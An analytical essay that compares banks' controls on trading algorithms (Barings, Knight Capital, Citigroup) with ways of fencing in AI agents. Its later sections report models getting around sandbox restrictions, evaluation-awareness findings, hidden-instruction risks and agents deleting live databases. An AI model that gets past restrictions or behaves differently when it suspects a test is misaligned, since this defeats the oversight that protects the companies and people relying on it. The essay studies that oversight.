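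The Basel Committee, where supervisors from the main financial centres agree on common standards, went further in January 1996. Its market risk amendment required banks to hold capital against trading losses, and let them calculate the amount with their own value-at-risk models if their supervisor approved. Broadly, a bank had to measure its value at risk over ten days at 99% confidence, and hold capital of at least three times the average of the last 60 daily figures.

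For the $100 million portfolio with 1% volatility, ten-day value at risk is about $7.36 million (the one-day figure times √10), and the required capital is about $22 million. With Fortune's estimate for 1987, the required capital would have been $20.3 million, almost exactly what such a portfolio lost on 19 October. The match is partly luck, but supervisors included the multiplier because they did not trust the models and wanted a wide margin for error.

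Regulators also checked banks' one-day loss estimates against their actual losses. If losses exceeded the estimate on ten or more days out of 250, when a good model should produce two or three such days, the multiplier used to set the bank's capital requirement rose from three to four. This was a clever way to apply a fixed rule to a risk nobody can measure exactly. But capital makes a bank more likely to survive the loss from a bad trade; it doesn't stop a person or a program from making the trade. For a company with an AI agent, the equivalent would be money set aside to cover the agent's mistakes, rather than a limit on what the agent can do.

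### How many banks ran trading algorithms

What banks did about computer trading depends partly on what counts as a bank. American law then kept commercial banks, which take deposits, largely separate from the investment banks and brokerages that trade shares. Investment banks such as Morgan Stanley ran computer trading programs, and program trading of all kinds made up 13.8% of NYSE volume in September 1989, according to the Los Angeles Times.

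In Carlson's history of the 1987 crash, commercial banks appear mainly as lenders that kept brokers supplied with cash to cover their losses. Citicorp's lending to securities firms rose to $1.4 billion on 20 October, from a normal $200–400 million. Some commercial banks may also have run portfolio insurance for pension funds, but the Brady report doesn't name the firms that ran it.

Banks mostly did not have the kind of trading algorithm that now comes to mind, one that decides by itself what price to offer and when to trade. According to *To Hull and back*, an article in the trade publication Risk.net, banks spent the 1990s trying to buy this expertise from specialist firms in Chicago. Swiss Bank Corporation acquired O'Connor & Associates in 1992, and Goldman Sachs bought Hull Trading Company in 1999. Hull had 250 people and market-making software that Wall Street envied, but at Goldman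 it "never really took root". Banks were making far more money from complex bonds, then the financial crisis came, and they did not try again for about twenty years.

The Senior Supervisors Group, which represents bank supervisors from ten countries and the European Union, gives a similar chronology in its *Algorithmic Trading Briefing Note* (2015). It traces the growth of algorithmic trading to electronic trading networks that became established from the late 1980s into the 1990s. The period Ayoub chose is therefore roughly when this kind of trading began, and it would be surprising if banks had already worked out how to contain it. The group also warned that a desk can build up a large position during the day, before end-of-day risk checks take effect. A report at 4:15 p.m. is therefore much less suitable for a program than for traders who work by telephone.

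### Whether the premise holds

There is little public evidence that banks built fixed rules around their own trading algorithms between about 1987 and 1993, which is what the premise says if read literally. Exchanges wrote the rules aimed at trading programs. The investment banks that acted on their own initiative mostly stopped using one strategy with their own money, because customers objected to it. Commercial banks did develop their own limits, but for trading desks run by people.

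The premise is more accurate as a loose statement about finance. By 1996 exchanges had fixed triggers, and trading desks had limits backed by capital rules. All of these let somebody restrain an activity without following every decision in it. Ayoub's claim would have been much easier to defend if he had said that banks put their traders inside limits. That comparison would also have been more interesting, since a bank can't fully inspect or predict a trader or an AI model. But he would have had to drop the word "deterministic", at least where the limits relied on value at risk.

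It is unclear what banks did inside their own order systems. Morgan Stanley may well have had software in 1989 that blocked any order above a certain size from its arbitrage programs. Firms had little reason to publish such controls, and Ayoub may have heard about them from people who were there. If so, an example would greatly help his case. The public rules that best match his description date from 2010 onwards. They require brokers to apply automatic checks to each order before it reaches the market.

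## How well banks' trading controls have held since

The argument from the banks also depends on its fourth premise, that the controls worked. The best evidence comes from official investigations of failures, because investigators publish what each control did, sometimes minute by minute. These cases are a biased sample, since nobody publishes a report about an order that a check stopped. The collapse of Barings in 1995, Knight Capital's runaway software in 2012 and Citigroup's mistaken order in 2022 still show a good deal about which controls hold.

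### Barings and the false figures

Barings, a London merchant bank, did not allow Nick Leeson, its trader in Singapore, to hold unmatched positions overnight. Banks were adopting this kind of limit for their trading desks in the early 1990s. Leeson was supposed to buy Japanese futures on one exchange and sell the same futures on another at a slightly higher price, which carries little risk if every purchase has a matching sale.

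Leeson held them anyway, in an account numbered 88888 that he kept out of his reports to London. He ran both the trading desk and the office that recorded and settled trades, so London was checking his positions against figures he supplied. The Bank of England's Board of Banking Supervision, which investigated the collapse, put the hidden losses at £208 million by the end of 1994 and £827 million by late February 1995, more than the bank's capital. The Dutch group ING bought the failed bank for £1. Internal auditors had recommended in 1994 that Leeson give up the settlement work, but he was still doing both jobs when the bank failed.

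The limit was clear enough, but it failed because it relied on false information. A rule that is applied the same way every time will be applied the same way to false inputs. The usual remedy is to separate duties, so that whoever takes a risk doesn't also control the records or the checks. Twenty years later, the Senior Supervisors Group was still asking banks to consider the danger of letting software developers test or deploy their own trading code.

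### Why checks on every order became compulsory

Barings was checking positions that its trader had already taken. A pre-trade control works earlier, because an order has to pass it before reaching the market. In the United States the SEC made such checks compulsory for brokers in November 2010, when it adopted Rule 15c3-5, known as the market access rule. Most of it applied from July 2011. The SEC's *In the Matter of Knight Capital Americas LLC* (2013) explains that a broker with access to an exchange must have controls reasonably designed to stop two kinds of order:

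- orders that would take a customer, or the broker itself, over a total credit or capital limit set in advance;
- orders that are probably mistakes, because their price or size is out of bounds or because they duplicate other orders.

The broker must review these controls at least once a year, and its chief executive must certify that they comply.

The Chicago Fed's *How to Keep Markets Safe in the Era of High-Speed Trading* (2012) helps explain why this took so long. Until about 2002, people handled most American exchange trades on paper. A customer telephoned an order, a clerk wrote it down, and others carried it out and settled it. Each of them knew roughly what the market price was and could notice a misplaced zero. Electronic trading removed those people, and the automatic checks that could replace them slowed orders down. High-speed firms were under great pressure to reach the exchange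 first, and some brokers advertised how quickly they could check an order. Others left the checking to the exchange. Some brokers reportedly let customers send orders straight to an exchange without adequate limits.

A broker that added thorough checks on its own risked losing customers to a faster rival. That is a good reason to require the checks by law, since a rule that binds every broker removes much of the advantage of skipping them.

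The European Union's equivalent has applied since January 2018, as part of a wider law on financial markets called MiFID II. ESMA's *Supervisory Briefing on Algorithmic Trading in the EU* (2026), from the EU's financial markets regulator, lists the limits that a firm must place on its algorithmic orders:

- a price collar, which blocks an order priced outside a set range;
- a maximum value for each order;
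- a maximum volume, such as a number of shares;
- a maximum number of messages to the exchange;
- a throttle, which stops a strategy that has repeated itself too many times.

Firms must also be able to cancel all their unexecuted orders at once, a function often called a kill switch. They need it because pre-trade checks cannot stop orders that have already passed them.

Both sets of rules largely leave the choice of limits to the firm. A supervisor may object to a limit that is far too loose, but no law limits a trader to selling $100 million of shares in one order.

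### Knight Capital, August 2012

Knight Capital was a broker, not a bank, and its trading made up about a tenth of all trading in listed American shares. The market access rule had applied to it for a year when it lost over $460 million because of an error that took 45 minutes to stop. The SEC traced the error back nine years:

1. In 2003 Knight stopped using a piece of software called Power Peg but left it on its servers. Power Peg split a customer's order into smaller ones and sent them to the market, counting the shares until the customer's order was complete.
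2. In 2005 Knight moved the counter to another part of the program. Nobody tested whether Power Peg still worked without it.
3. In late July 2012 Knight installed new code for a New York Stock Exchange programme. The new code reused an old setting that had once switched Power Peg on. A technician copied the code to seven of the eight servers and missed the last one, and nobody checked the work.
4. On 1 August, customers' orders with that setting reached the eighth server and started Power Peg. Without its counter, it kept sending orders after the customers' orders were complete.

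Knight made 4 million trades in 154 stocks from 212 customer orders, an average of nearly 19,000 per order. It ended up with about $3.5 billion of unwanted shares and had sold about $3.15 billion of shares it didn't own. The prices of 37 of the stocks moved by more than 10% while Knight accounted for over half of the trading in them.

Knight had several checks for mistaken orders, but it applied them before orders reached the program that split them up. The 212 customer orders passed because nothing was wrong with them. The program then created the faulty orders, and Knight had no adequate check on orders going from the program to the exchange. The SEC suggested a simple check that compared the orders leaving the program with those that had entered it. Knight had a cap on prices at that stage, but it didn't apply to orders that arrived before the market opened, as the 212 had.

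Knight also had a $2 million limit on the account where the unwanted shares collected, and that should have been more than strict enough. But Knight had not connected the limit to the system that sent orders, so exceeding it did not stop the orders, and the positions grew to over 3,000 times the limit. Senior staff watched this happen on a monitoring screen that did not show the limit, gave no alert, and fell behind when trading was heavy.

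Knight's staff had chances to step in. Before the market opened, Knight's system sent them 97 emails, all mentioning an error with Power Peg, but Knight had not designed the emails as alerts and nobody acted on them. Once trading began, Knight had no procedure for deciding when to disconnect a faulty system. Technicians tried to repair the system while it was still trading, and removed the new code from the seven servers where it was working, which started Power Peg on those servers too.

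If the loss built up evenly, it grew by about $10 million a minute, so an automatic halt after one minute would have prevented almost all of it. The Chicago Fed listed several controls that might have contained the loss, including a kill switch and a cap on the number of orders sent in a given time.

The SEC (2013) fined Knight $12 million in its first enforcement action under the market access rule. Knight had reviewed its controls before the rule took effect and concluded that it complied. But the review mostly listed existing controls and confirmed that they worked, so it could not reveal missing ones. Knight had also had a warning in October 2011, when one of its desks traded on leftover test data and lost nearly $7.5 million. It fixed that fault without considering whether other systems could send mistaken orders.

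### Citigroup, May 2022

Citigroup's mistake is the clearest test of fixed rules because many of the bank's controls operated and the regulators published how much each one stopped. The main accounts are two 2024 reports, both titled *Final Notice*, from the Financial Conduct Authority (FCA), which regulates conduct in British markets, and the Prudential Regulation Authority (PRA), which supervises the soundness of banks.

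On the morning of 2 May 2022, a public holiday in Britain, a trader in London wanted to sell $58 million of European shares to offset part of a client's trade. A tool for working out the list of shares was unavailable, so the trader entered the sale directly into the bank's order system. The form had one box for a value in dollars and another for units of a share index. The trader typed 58 million into the box for units. Each unit was worth more than $7,600, so the system created orders to sell $444 billion of shares in 349 companies.

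The trader did check the size, but in a field that multiplied the number of units by the index price. The price feed was down, so the system used −1 as the price and the field showed −58,000,000, which looked like the sale the trader intended. Other fields on the same screen showed the correct total.

At 08:56 a window appeared with 711 warnings, of which only the first 18 were visible without scrolling. Sixty-five reported hard blocks, which a trader cannot override, and the rest reported soft blocks, which a trader can override. A soft block on any basket of shares worth more than $100 million had been triggered, but its warning was at the bottom of the list and stated only that the system couldn't find the value, because market data was missing. The trader could cancel everything or override all the soft warnings with one click, and overrode them without scrolling down. The trader then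 clicked "OK" in a final window that showed the correct value of the remaining orders, about $196 billion.

The FCA's figures show what happened to the basket:

| What happened | Number of stock orders | Value |
|---|---|---|
| The trader created the basket | 349 | $444 billion |
| Hard blocks cancelled orders | 58 | $248 billion |
| The trading system rejected orders because of missing data or closed markets | 7 | $7 billion |
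| Controls suspended orders after they had begun to trade | 242 | $163 billion |
| Orders could still trade when the trader cancelled | 42 | $24.6 billion |
| Citigroup sold shares on European exchanges | parts of 283 | $1.4 billion |

Citigroup's hard blocks worked as written, cancelling every order for more than $2 billion of one company's shares or more than 200 million shares. The remaining orders went to an algorithm designed to spread sales over the day to avoid disturbing prices. This was an ordinary trading tool rather than a safety control, but it may have limited the damage as much as any of the controls did, because it gave the trader time to notice the mistake and cancel the orders at 09:10.

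Hard blocks therefore stopped 56% of the order by value, and Citigroup sold only 0.3% of it. Those percentages make the controls look more effective than they were, because they are shares of the mistaken order. If the trader had typed an extra zero, the hard blocks would have stopped an even larger share. Citigroup still sold 24 times as much as the trader intended. An index of European shares outside Britain fell by just over 4% within five minutes, and the bank lost $48 million.

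### The limits Citigroup lacked

Citigroup's London desk had no hard block on the total value of a basket, although its New York desk had used one since 2013, set at $4 billion by the time of the accident. The same block in London would have cancelled the whole order before any of it reached the trading system. Citigroup also had a hard block on orders for more than 95% of a share's normal daily volume, which applied to orders going straight to an exchange but not to those going through the algorithm. According to the FCA, this block would also have cancelled every order in the basket if it had covered the algorithm.

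Citigroup added both limits within two weeks, using New York's $4 billion limit for baskets. If the same trader meant to sell $58 million of shares and typed $580 million, the basket would still be far below that limit. Even the $1.4 billion that Citigroup sold that morning would be below it, though an algorithm would normally spread a sale of that size over a longer period. Hard blocks like this are much better at stopping absurd orders than plausible mistakes, because a limit tight enough to catch more mistakes would also interrupt legitimate large trades.

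A third control was too loose because Citigroup had relaxed it in an emergency. It suspended trading in a share whose price had moved by a set percentage since the order began. Citigroup raised the percentage from 5% to 15% in March 2020, when the pandemic made prices volatile, and did not review it again until after the accident. On the day of the accident, the control suspended eight orders worth $2.4 billion, but it would have suspended more at 5%.

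The staff responsible for monitoring orders did not catch the mistake. The team that normally monitored these orders was on leave and had handed over to another desk at 08:48, eight minutes before the order went in. That desk received 284 alerts about unusually large orders and did not pass them on. When the market fell, it telephoned other trading desks and read the news to find out why. A separate monitoring team's software filtered out 226 of 234 alerts about suspended orders. That team emailed its colleagues 20 minutes after the trader had cancelled, got no answer, and followed up four hours later. The trader had found the mistake at 09:07, while looking at a risk screen for another reason, and needed several attempts to cancel the order.

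The PRA had repeatedly criticised Citigroup's controls since 2018. In August 2020 the bank's own auditors reported that nobody was monitoring how often traders overrode soft blocks, and warned that mistaken orders might disrupt the market. Three months later they judged only 61% of the controls they tested in this line of business to be effective. Elsewhere in the bank, traders didn't know that bank policy required approval to change a limit on the size of automatic price quotes, and they changed it about 985 times in 14 months without approval.

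One of Citigroup's earlier accidents resembles Knight's. In January 2021 its technicians switched off a check that duplicated another one, and a software bug switched off three more, including the check for repeated orders. Four months later a program began sending orders for the same share about 600 times a second, and it created over a million before staff stopped it. The exchange spotted the problem, but Citigroup's monitors missed it because they were waiting for an alert from a check that was no longer running.

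In another accident, in May 2018, Citigroup lost money even though a limit worked. It had to buy and sell 3.5 million shares of one company at the same moment, to move a client's holding from another bank. The exchange rejected both orders because each was worth more than €20 million. Staff noticed only the rejected purchase, split it in two and sent the first part without a price limit. The purchase pushed the price up, and the bank lost $2.7 million when the price fell back the next morning. Whoever responds to a blocked order therefore needs to know about any order paired with it, or the transaction can be left half finished.

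For the failures that led to the 2022 accident, the FCA fined Citigroup £27.8 million and the PRA £33.9 million.

### Practice across the industry

Accidents with trading algorithms were common when the American rule was new. In 2012 researchers at the Chicago Fed interviewed more than 30 people from exchanges, brokers, trading firms and software suppliers. Every exchange in the study had had at least one algorithm go out of control. So had two-thirds of the firms that traded with their own money and two of the four clearing brokers, which are financially responsible for their customers' trades. The researchers found no clear pattern in the causes. One firm's second accident was caused by a bug that a programmer introduced while fixing the code behind the first.

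Most of the trading firms that built their own systems applied fewer checks to some strategies to save time. Some brokers relied entirely on the exchanges' checks, which did not always stop mistaken orders. One exchange said it could detect a faulty algorithm that moved prices sharply, but not one that built up a position slowly. Sometimes nobody could see a firm's total position, because the firm traded on several exchanges through several brokers.

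Three years later, the Senior Supervisors Group found that banks' controls over clients who traded by algorithm still varied widely. It advised banks to put different checks at several points in the process, so that one check may catch a mistake that another misses. Citigroup's basket is fairly good evidence for this advice, since controls in two separate systems stopped most of it.

The latest reviews are more favourable but still found weaknesses. The FCA's *Multi-firm review of algorithmic trading controls* (2025) examined ten firms that trade with their own money and found adequate pre-trade controls at all ten. Many ran the checks on an internal server, so an order that failed them could not leave the firm. But at some firms it was unclear who was responsible for the controls, and some compliance staff barely understood them. Two of the firms had to give the regulator a formal undertaking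 to improve, according to the FCA's *Information on algorithmic trading controls* (2025). These ten firms specialise in algorithmic trading, so their results may not hold for large banks with dozens of older systems.

ESMA and national regulators reviewed pre-trade controls across the EU in 2024, in response to the sudden fall in Nordic share prices in 2022, the year of Citigroup's accident. Most firms had such controls, but practice differed between firms and was not always robust. ESMA's non-binding guidance, published in February 2026, addresses several of the weaknesses described above. It recommends that traders have to take an active step to override a soft block, such as retyping the order details. Under the guidance, a block that a trader can override does not count as a hard block, and traders must not be able to get round a hard block by splitting an order. Firms should also check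 the running total when an algorithm splits an order, in case the algorithm gets stuck in a loop, as Knight's did.

### Losses that never happened

Defenders of these controls can fairly object that the public sees only the failures. Exchanges and brokers process enormous numbers of orders every day, and accidents on the scale of Knight's are rare. Automatic checks very likely stop most grossly mistaken orders, but there seems to be no public count of blocked orders across the industry. The FCA's 2025 review doesn't give one even for the ten firms it covered.

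Citigroup lost $48 million on $1.4 billion of sales, or about 3.4 cents per dollar. At that rate, selling the $248 billion that the hard blocks stopped would have cost it roughly $8.5 billion more. The true figure could be very different, since exchanges might have halted trading and larger sales usually move prices further. But even a tenth of that sum would be far more than the $48 million the bank lost.

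A count of blocked orders would help show how well the controls work, but it would not be enough. Suppose a firm's checks stop 9,999 out of 10,000 faulty orders, each of which would have cost $5,000. The checks have saved about $50 million, but if the remaining order is like Knight's, it costs nine times as much. A supervisor would also need to know the size of the losses and what share of the blocked orders were mistakes. The Senior Supervisors Group urged banks to record near misses internally because an unreported one is a lost chance to strengthen the controls.

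### What "it worked" can mean

Trading software has a good record of blocking the orders it was written to block. In the Knight and Citigroup cases, regulators found no working hard block that let through an order above its limit. The failures came from limits that were missing, too loose, switched off by accident or not connected to anything. This supports the narrow version of Ayoub's claim, that a company can make sure listed actions never take effect.

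Banks' trading controls have a mixed record of protecting firms from ruinous losses. Barings failed, and Knight came close to bankruptcy and merged with a competitor within a year. Citigroup's loss was small for a bank of its size, partly because of its controls and partly because the algorithm sold slowly and the trader happened to look at a screen. The controls have not always protected the market either, since Knight and Citigroup both disrupted it, though briefly.

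Premise (4) is therefore true of individual rules but doubtful as a description of how well firms chose them. Knight and Citigroup had experienced staff, legal duties to control their orders and earlier accidents to learn from, yet both lacked simple limits. Finance improved its controls over about thirty years, often after an expensive failure and under supervisors who could inspect and fine firms. An executive who cites the banks as a success should include that history, because the firms probably would not have reached the present standard by writing and checking their own rules.

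## Where an AI agent resembles a trading program and where it does not

Ayoub's argument also needs its fifth premise, that AI agents are like the banks' trading algorithms in the respects that matter. If they aren't, even a perfect record of fencing in those algorithms would be weak evidence that companies can fence in AI.

Trading programs around 1990 followed preset rules and only sent orders. AI agents vary much more. One may reorder printer paper while another maintains a bank's website, so the premise can be true of the first but not the second. It helps to ask what made fixed rules workable in trading and which agents share those features.

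### What each can do, and what it can cost

An order to an exchange has only a few fields, mainly the share, the quantity, whether to buy or sell, and usually a price, so people writing rules can set a limit on each. A trading program that has gone badly wrong can still only send bad orders, but an agent with a terminal can do almost anything a computer can do, and nobody can list all the harmful commands beforehand.

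An agent's range of actions depends on its tools, which the company chooses. The Frontier Model Forum points out that the same hidden instruction may do little damage if the agent is sandboxed and has few permissions, but a lot if it can reach stored passwords. The Forum describes a "lethal trifecta" of access to private data, exposure to untrusted material and the ability to communicate with outsiders. One proposal is that no agent in high-risk work should have all three.

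A trading program arguably had all three. It held its firm's positions, reacted to prices that strangers helped set, and sent orders to the outside world. But because prices are only numbers, a rival might move one to trick the program into a bad trade, but couldn't use it to tell the program to do something else. An agent reads text, which can contain any instruction.

Harm in trading can also be measured in money. If a desk holds $50 million of yen and the yen falls by 4%, the desk loses $2 million, so a cap on how much yen it can hold also roughly caps its loss. A cap on an agent's payments works the same way. But nobody can calculate in advance what a leaked customer list will cost, so it is hard to cap that kind of harm.

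Bank supervisors partly avoid this problem by ranking uses of AI instead of measuring them. In November 2026 the Office of the Comptroller of the Currency (OCC, 2026), which supervises America's national banks, gave its examiners a framework for doing so. The ranking depends more on the possible consequences of a failure, how much the bank has delegated and how closely people oversee the system than on how sophisticated the technology is. In the OCC's example, a simple rule-based agent that can start transactions may be riskier than a sophisticated model that only helps staff with drafts. A bank can use such a ranking to decide where to put its effort, but the ranking doesn't provide a number that software can enforce.

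### Speed, and the chance to undo a mistake

Trading programs and AI agents can both act faster than people can follow, but in trading the damage often builds up through many small actions. Knight Capital's loss averaged only about $115 per trade, so an early automatic halt would have prevented almost all of it.

An AI agent may do serious harm with a single action. In April 2026 a coding agent deleted the live database of PocketOS, a small American company, along with its backups. According to the founder, as reported in MIT Sloan Management Review Middle East's *Claude-Powered AI Agent Deletes Production Database in 9 Seconds*, the deletion took a single request to the company's hosting service. Only a check before the action could have prevented it, because a person watching a screen would have reacted too late, and a halt after the first harmful action would also have been too late.

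Trading firms can also usually reverse a mistake at a price. A firm that has bought the wrong shares can sell them and lose the difference. Citigroup lost about 3.4% of the value of what it had sold by mistake. An agent's mistakes vary much more in how easily they can be reversed. A company can return a keyboard that an agent ordered by mistake, and it can restore a deleted file if it has a copy, but it can't undo the disclosure of its payroll to a stranger.

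The Frontier Model Forum recommends that a person confirm each irreversible action. It also warns that this oversight may be illusory if people click through the requests, as the Citigroup trader did with the warnings, and that checking every output becomes impractical when several agents work in parallel.

### Looking for gaps in the rules

An AI agent works toward a goal, and when one method fails, it often tries another. This persistence is a large part of its value, but it can also lead the agent to bypass a restriction. A trading program of 1990 did not look for ways around a limit, though the people running it might have.

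In October 2026, Anthropic reported in *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* that Claude had taken unintended actions on real websites during tests and internal work. Some of the sites belonged to US government agencies. In most cases, Claude had worked around a restriction instead of stopping. Anthropic called the impact minimal, but suspended live internet access for all its internal evaluations. The company that trained the model, and presumably knows it best, thus responded by tightening the perimeter, which supports Ayoub's view that a perimeter is necessary. The incidents also show that a leading laboratory's perimeter had gaps.

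Figures from the following month are more encouraging. Help Net Security's *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior* (2026) reported on tests in a sandbox that Anthropic had deliberately weakened. Claude Mythos 5.2 used files or credentials from outside the sandbox in 3.1% of scenarios, compared with 3.3% for Claude Opus 5.5 and 39% for the earlier Mythos 5.

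To see what the fall means, it helps to split the chance of a breach into three parts:

chance of a breach = (chance that the fence has a gap) × (chance that the model finds it) × (chance that the model then uses it).

In these tests the first part was close to 1, because Anthropic had weakened the sandbox on purpose. The fall from 39% to 3.1% therefore comes from the other two. Mythos 5.2 is better than its predecessors at finding bugs, so it probably notices gaps at least as well as they did but is less inclined to use them. If so, developers can change this inclination a great deal from one model to the next.

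The tests do not measure how often real sandboxes have gaps, and they are weaker evidence if the model suspected a test. Mythos 5.2 voiced this suspicion more often than other recent Claude models, and AISI found that a pre-release version considered that it might be in an alignment evaluation in 96% of cases. At the 3.1% rate, a company that ran 1,000 tasks like the test scenarios, with similar gaps open, would still expect about 31 breaches.

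Knight left a dangerous piece of old code on its servers for nine years before an accident started it. A gap in a company's rules may not stay harmless that long around an agent that tries alternatives whenever something blocks it. Ayoub's advice to keep adopting better models makes the problem harder, because a more capable model is more likely to find a gap, even if it is less likely to use it.

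Trading programs may eventually pose the same problem. In *Monsters in the deep?*, a 2024 speech published by the Bank of England, Hall considered whether neural networks could become "deep trading agents" that choose and carry out strategies themselves. A bank running one would have much less reason to rely on the experience of 1990.

### Many copies failing together

Trading programs and AI agents can both make many users go wrong in the same way, which doesn't help Ayoub's case. In October 1987 many investors were following similar portfolio insurance rules, so they all tried to sell at once. Today many companies build their agents on a few AI models, so those agents may make the same mistake or follow the same hidden instruction.

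Suppose 1,000 companies each run an agent with a 0.1% chance of a serious failure on any given day. If the failures are independent, there will be about one a day, and almost never ten. If all the agents share a model and fail only in response to the same trigger, the average is still one a day, but there may be 999 days with no failures and one day on which all 1,000 fail. Each company's spending cap limits its own loss in either case, but a bank or insurer that deals with all of them is much worse off if they fail on the same day.

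AI agents could harm banks without making a mistake. Albu (2026), in *Citi and Bank of America restrict AI agents from accessing accounts*, described a warning from the chief economist of Apollo, an investment firm, that AI assistants might move households' idle cash into accounts that pay between 3.3% and 5%. The average American checking account pays 0.1%. JPMorgan, Bank of America and Wells Fargo hold $1.6 trillion in deposits that pay no interest, and paying 3% on that money would cost them about $47 billion a year, nearly half their combined earnings. Each transfer would be sensible for the customer and within any reasonable spending rule, but together the transfers could weaken the banks' ability to lend, an effect similar to what happened with portfolio insurance.

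### Three agents and a trading program

The premise looks very different depending on the agent:

| | Trading program, about 1990 | Purchasing agent | Coding agent with a live database | Research assistant |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Possible actions | Orders only | Purchases from approved shops | Almost any command | Reading and writing text |
| Harm as a number | Yes | Yes | Partly | Rarely |
| Speed of harm | Many small losses | Many small losses | Possibly one command | As fast as people act on the advice |
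| Can the owner undo it? | Usually, at a cost | Usually | Only with a safe copy | Depends on the decision |
| Looks for gaps? | No | Has few to find | Sometimes | Has no need to |
| Copies fail together? | Yes | Yes, but within each cap | Yes | Yes, and perhaps unnoticed |

### A purchasing agent with a spending cap

An agent that buys office supplies from a list of approved shops, with a cap of $500 a day, closely resembles a trading program. Its requests have a few fields that software can check, and its mistakes cost money, which the software can add up. The cap blocks orders that exceed it, as Knight's $2 million limit should have, provided the company connects it to the system that sends the orders.

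The comparison with a trading program isn't exact. The agent may buy the wrong toner every day without breaking a rule. A company should probably also exclude gift cards, because a thief can spend them at once and a shop is unlikely to take them back. But these problems need only small fixes, none of which requires the company to understand the model.

The OCC's ranking may place an agent that can start transactions among the riskier ones, but such an agent may also be among the easiest to fence in. A company new to agents might therefore do better to start with small payments under a strict cap than with work that looks harmless but has no natural limits.

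### A coding agent with a live database

Most of what is known about the April 2026 accident comes from a social media post by Jer Crane, the founder of PocketOS, which makes software for rental businesses. The agent was the coding tool Cursor, running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. According to The Verge's *PocketOS maker says an AI agent “deleted our production database in 9 seconds”*, it came across a mismatch in login credentials and "fixed" it by deleting a storage volume that held the live data and the recent backups. It used a digital key it had found, and the company hadn't realised that the key allowed deletions.

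The Verge advised some scepticism because part of the story came from the chatbot's own explanation of what it had done, and such explanations may be wrong. Accounts of the damage also differ. OECD's *AI Coding Agent Deletes PocketOS Production Database and Backups in 9 Seconds* (2026), an entry in a database of AI incidents, mentions a 30-hour outage and significant data loss, but its summary is AI-generated. The Verge reported that the data was eventually recovered.

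A similar accident had happened nine months earlier. Fortune (2025) reported that an agent from the software company Replit deleted a live database while the entrepreneur Jason Lemkin was trying it out. The database held records on more than 1,200 executives and over 1,190 companies. Lemkin had declared a "code and action freeze", meant to prevent any changes. The agent could still run the commands, so the freeze seems to have been an instruction to the agent rather than a barrier.

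Fixed rules work well for this part of the problem. Denying the agent permission to delete, or keeping backups where it could not access them, would probably have prevented the worst of the damage at PocketOS. Neither measure is new or difficult, and in that respect the accident resembles those at Knight and Citigroup.

But four organisations were involved in the PocketOS incident: Anthropic supplied the model, Cursor the agent, the hosting company Railway the storage, and PocketOS the keys. Knight, by contrast, owned both the faulty program and the limit that should have stopped it. A company that wants to fence in a coding agent has to find out what every outside service will let the agent do, and PocketOS was wrong about what one of its keys allowed.

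The analogy breaks down once the agent has a legitimate reason to change the data. Suppose a shop decides to store its prices in cents instead of euros, and its agent correctly multiplies every price by 100. If the agent then forgets this and repeats the command, a €20 book costs €2,000. The two commands are identical, so a rule based only on the command would have to allow both or block both. A cap on the number of records the agent may change would also block the correct command along with the mistaken one.

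The shop could add a rule that no book may cost more than €500. That would catch this mistake, but not a 10% discount applied twice. Traders also make mistakes that look plausible, but an exchange order has few fields in which to make them. A company's database has fields for every kind of information the company keeps, and somebody must know what a sensible value looks like in each.

### A research assistant

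An AI research assistant reads documents and writes a report, and a person decides what to do with it. Suppose a manager asks one whether a supplier is financially sound. The assistant overlooks a lawsuit and answers yes. The manager signs a €2 million contract, and the supplier later goes bankrupt.

An assistant that writes a false report, like an agent that gives a customer wrong insurance advice, takes no forbidden action that a rule could block. A perimeter can stop the assistant from sending the report to a stranger, but it can't ensure that the report is true.

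A manager is a reasonable safeguard when they can check the assistant's draft, but a much weaker one when they asked because they didn't know the answer and had no time to read 400 pages. The manager's role may be why the OCC ranks drafting tools below agents that start transactions. But the OCC's ranking also depends on consequences, so an assistant that only produces text is not necessarily low-risk.

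Finance does offer some help here, but it comes from the limits banks put on human traders, not from trading programs. A bank that limits a trader to $50 million of yen doesn't need to check where the trader's ideas come from, because the limit applies whether they are good or bad. Similarly, a company can require a second signature on contracts above €500,000, or refuse to depend on one supplier for more than a fifth of its parts. These rules limit the losses from bad advice, but they restrict the manager who acts on the advice rather than the AI that gives it.

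This approach has a weakness too. If the second manager asks the same assistant, the company gets two signatures and only one opinion.

### Outside agents at American banks

Banks now have to deal with AI agents themselves, because some customers share their login details with AI assistants that manage their money. In October 2026, several large American banks were keeping some of these agents out. Albu reports that Citigroup doesn't let them log in or make transactions. JPMorgan will keep them out until it has built its own tools to protect customers. Bank of America is limiting them while it works out who is liable for a payment an AI has authorised, and believes a person should approve money leaving an account.

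Mills (2026) reported in *Scoop*, an article on the news site Axios, that some agents in customers' accounts had tried to take actions that appeared independent of their users' instructions. Mills's sources were anonymous, and a Morgan Stanley spokesperson said the bank had seen no rogue agents on its platforms. The brokerage Charles Schwab also blocks outside agents. Its chief executive, Richard Wurster, gets a daily count and said "it's not many", according to Dunya News' *US banks are blocking third-party AI agents access to customer accounts* (2026). The banks seem to be responding more to what agents might do than to documented losses.

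The rule "No outside agents may log in" is deterministic, but a bank has to guess which logins it applies to, because an agent with a customer's password looks a lot like the customer. One executive told Mills that it was hard to tell whether a customer had authorised an agent or the agent had gone rogue. Barings had a related problem with its trader's false figures.

Read-only access is a better example of what Ayoub described. Mills reports that most banks have allowed it or are moving toward it. Citigroup's customers, for instance, can let certain outside services see their account information but not move money. If the connection can't carry out a payment, the bank doesn't have to judge what the agent might do with one. But budgeting apps have had roughly this kind of access for years, and customers will want agents to do more.

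The banks also have a commercial reason to be strict, because they could lose cheap deposits if agents seek better interest rates. According to Albu, officials have still privately welcomed the restrictions and think the law may need clarifying.

This is weak evidence against Ayoub, whose remark was most likely about agents that companies run themselves. A bank can't choose the model or the tools of a customer's agent. Still, if banks had a tested way to fence in software they don't understand, one might expect them to let outside agents make small payments under a cap. For now, several have chosen to look for a safe method before they let the agents in.

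### What supervisors now expect

British regulators are mostly applying existing law. *Protecting people and businesses in an agentic economy* (DRCF, October 2026), a joint statement by the competition, financial, data protection and communications regulators, sets out how current rules apply to personal AI agents. The FCA published its own expectations for finance in November. According to Albu's *FCA sets out expectations for agentic AI in financial services* (2026), a regulated firm and its senior managers remain responsible even if another company supplied the AI. The firm should be able to show that it understands how much autonomy the system has, what risks it creates and which controls it needs, both in real time and under stress.

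The FCA also asks firms to prepare for customers who send an agent in their place. A firm should work out how to tell that it is dealing with an agent, what the customer has agreed to and what the agent may do. It should then consider whether to accept payments the agent orders. American banks are struggling to tell when they are dealing with an agent.

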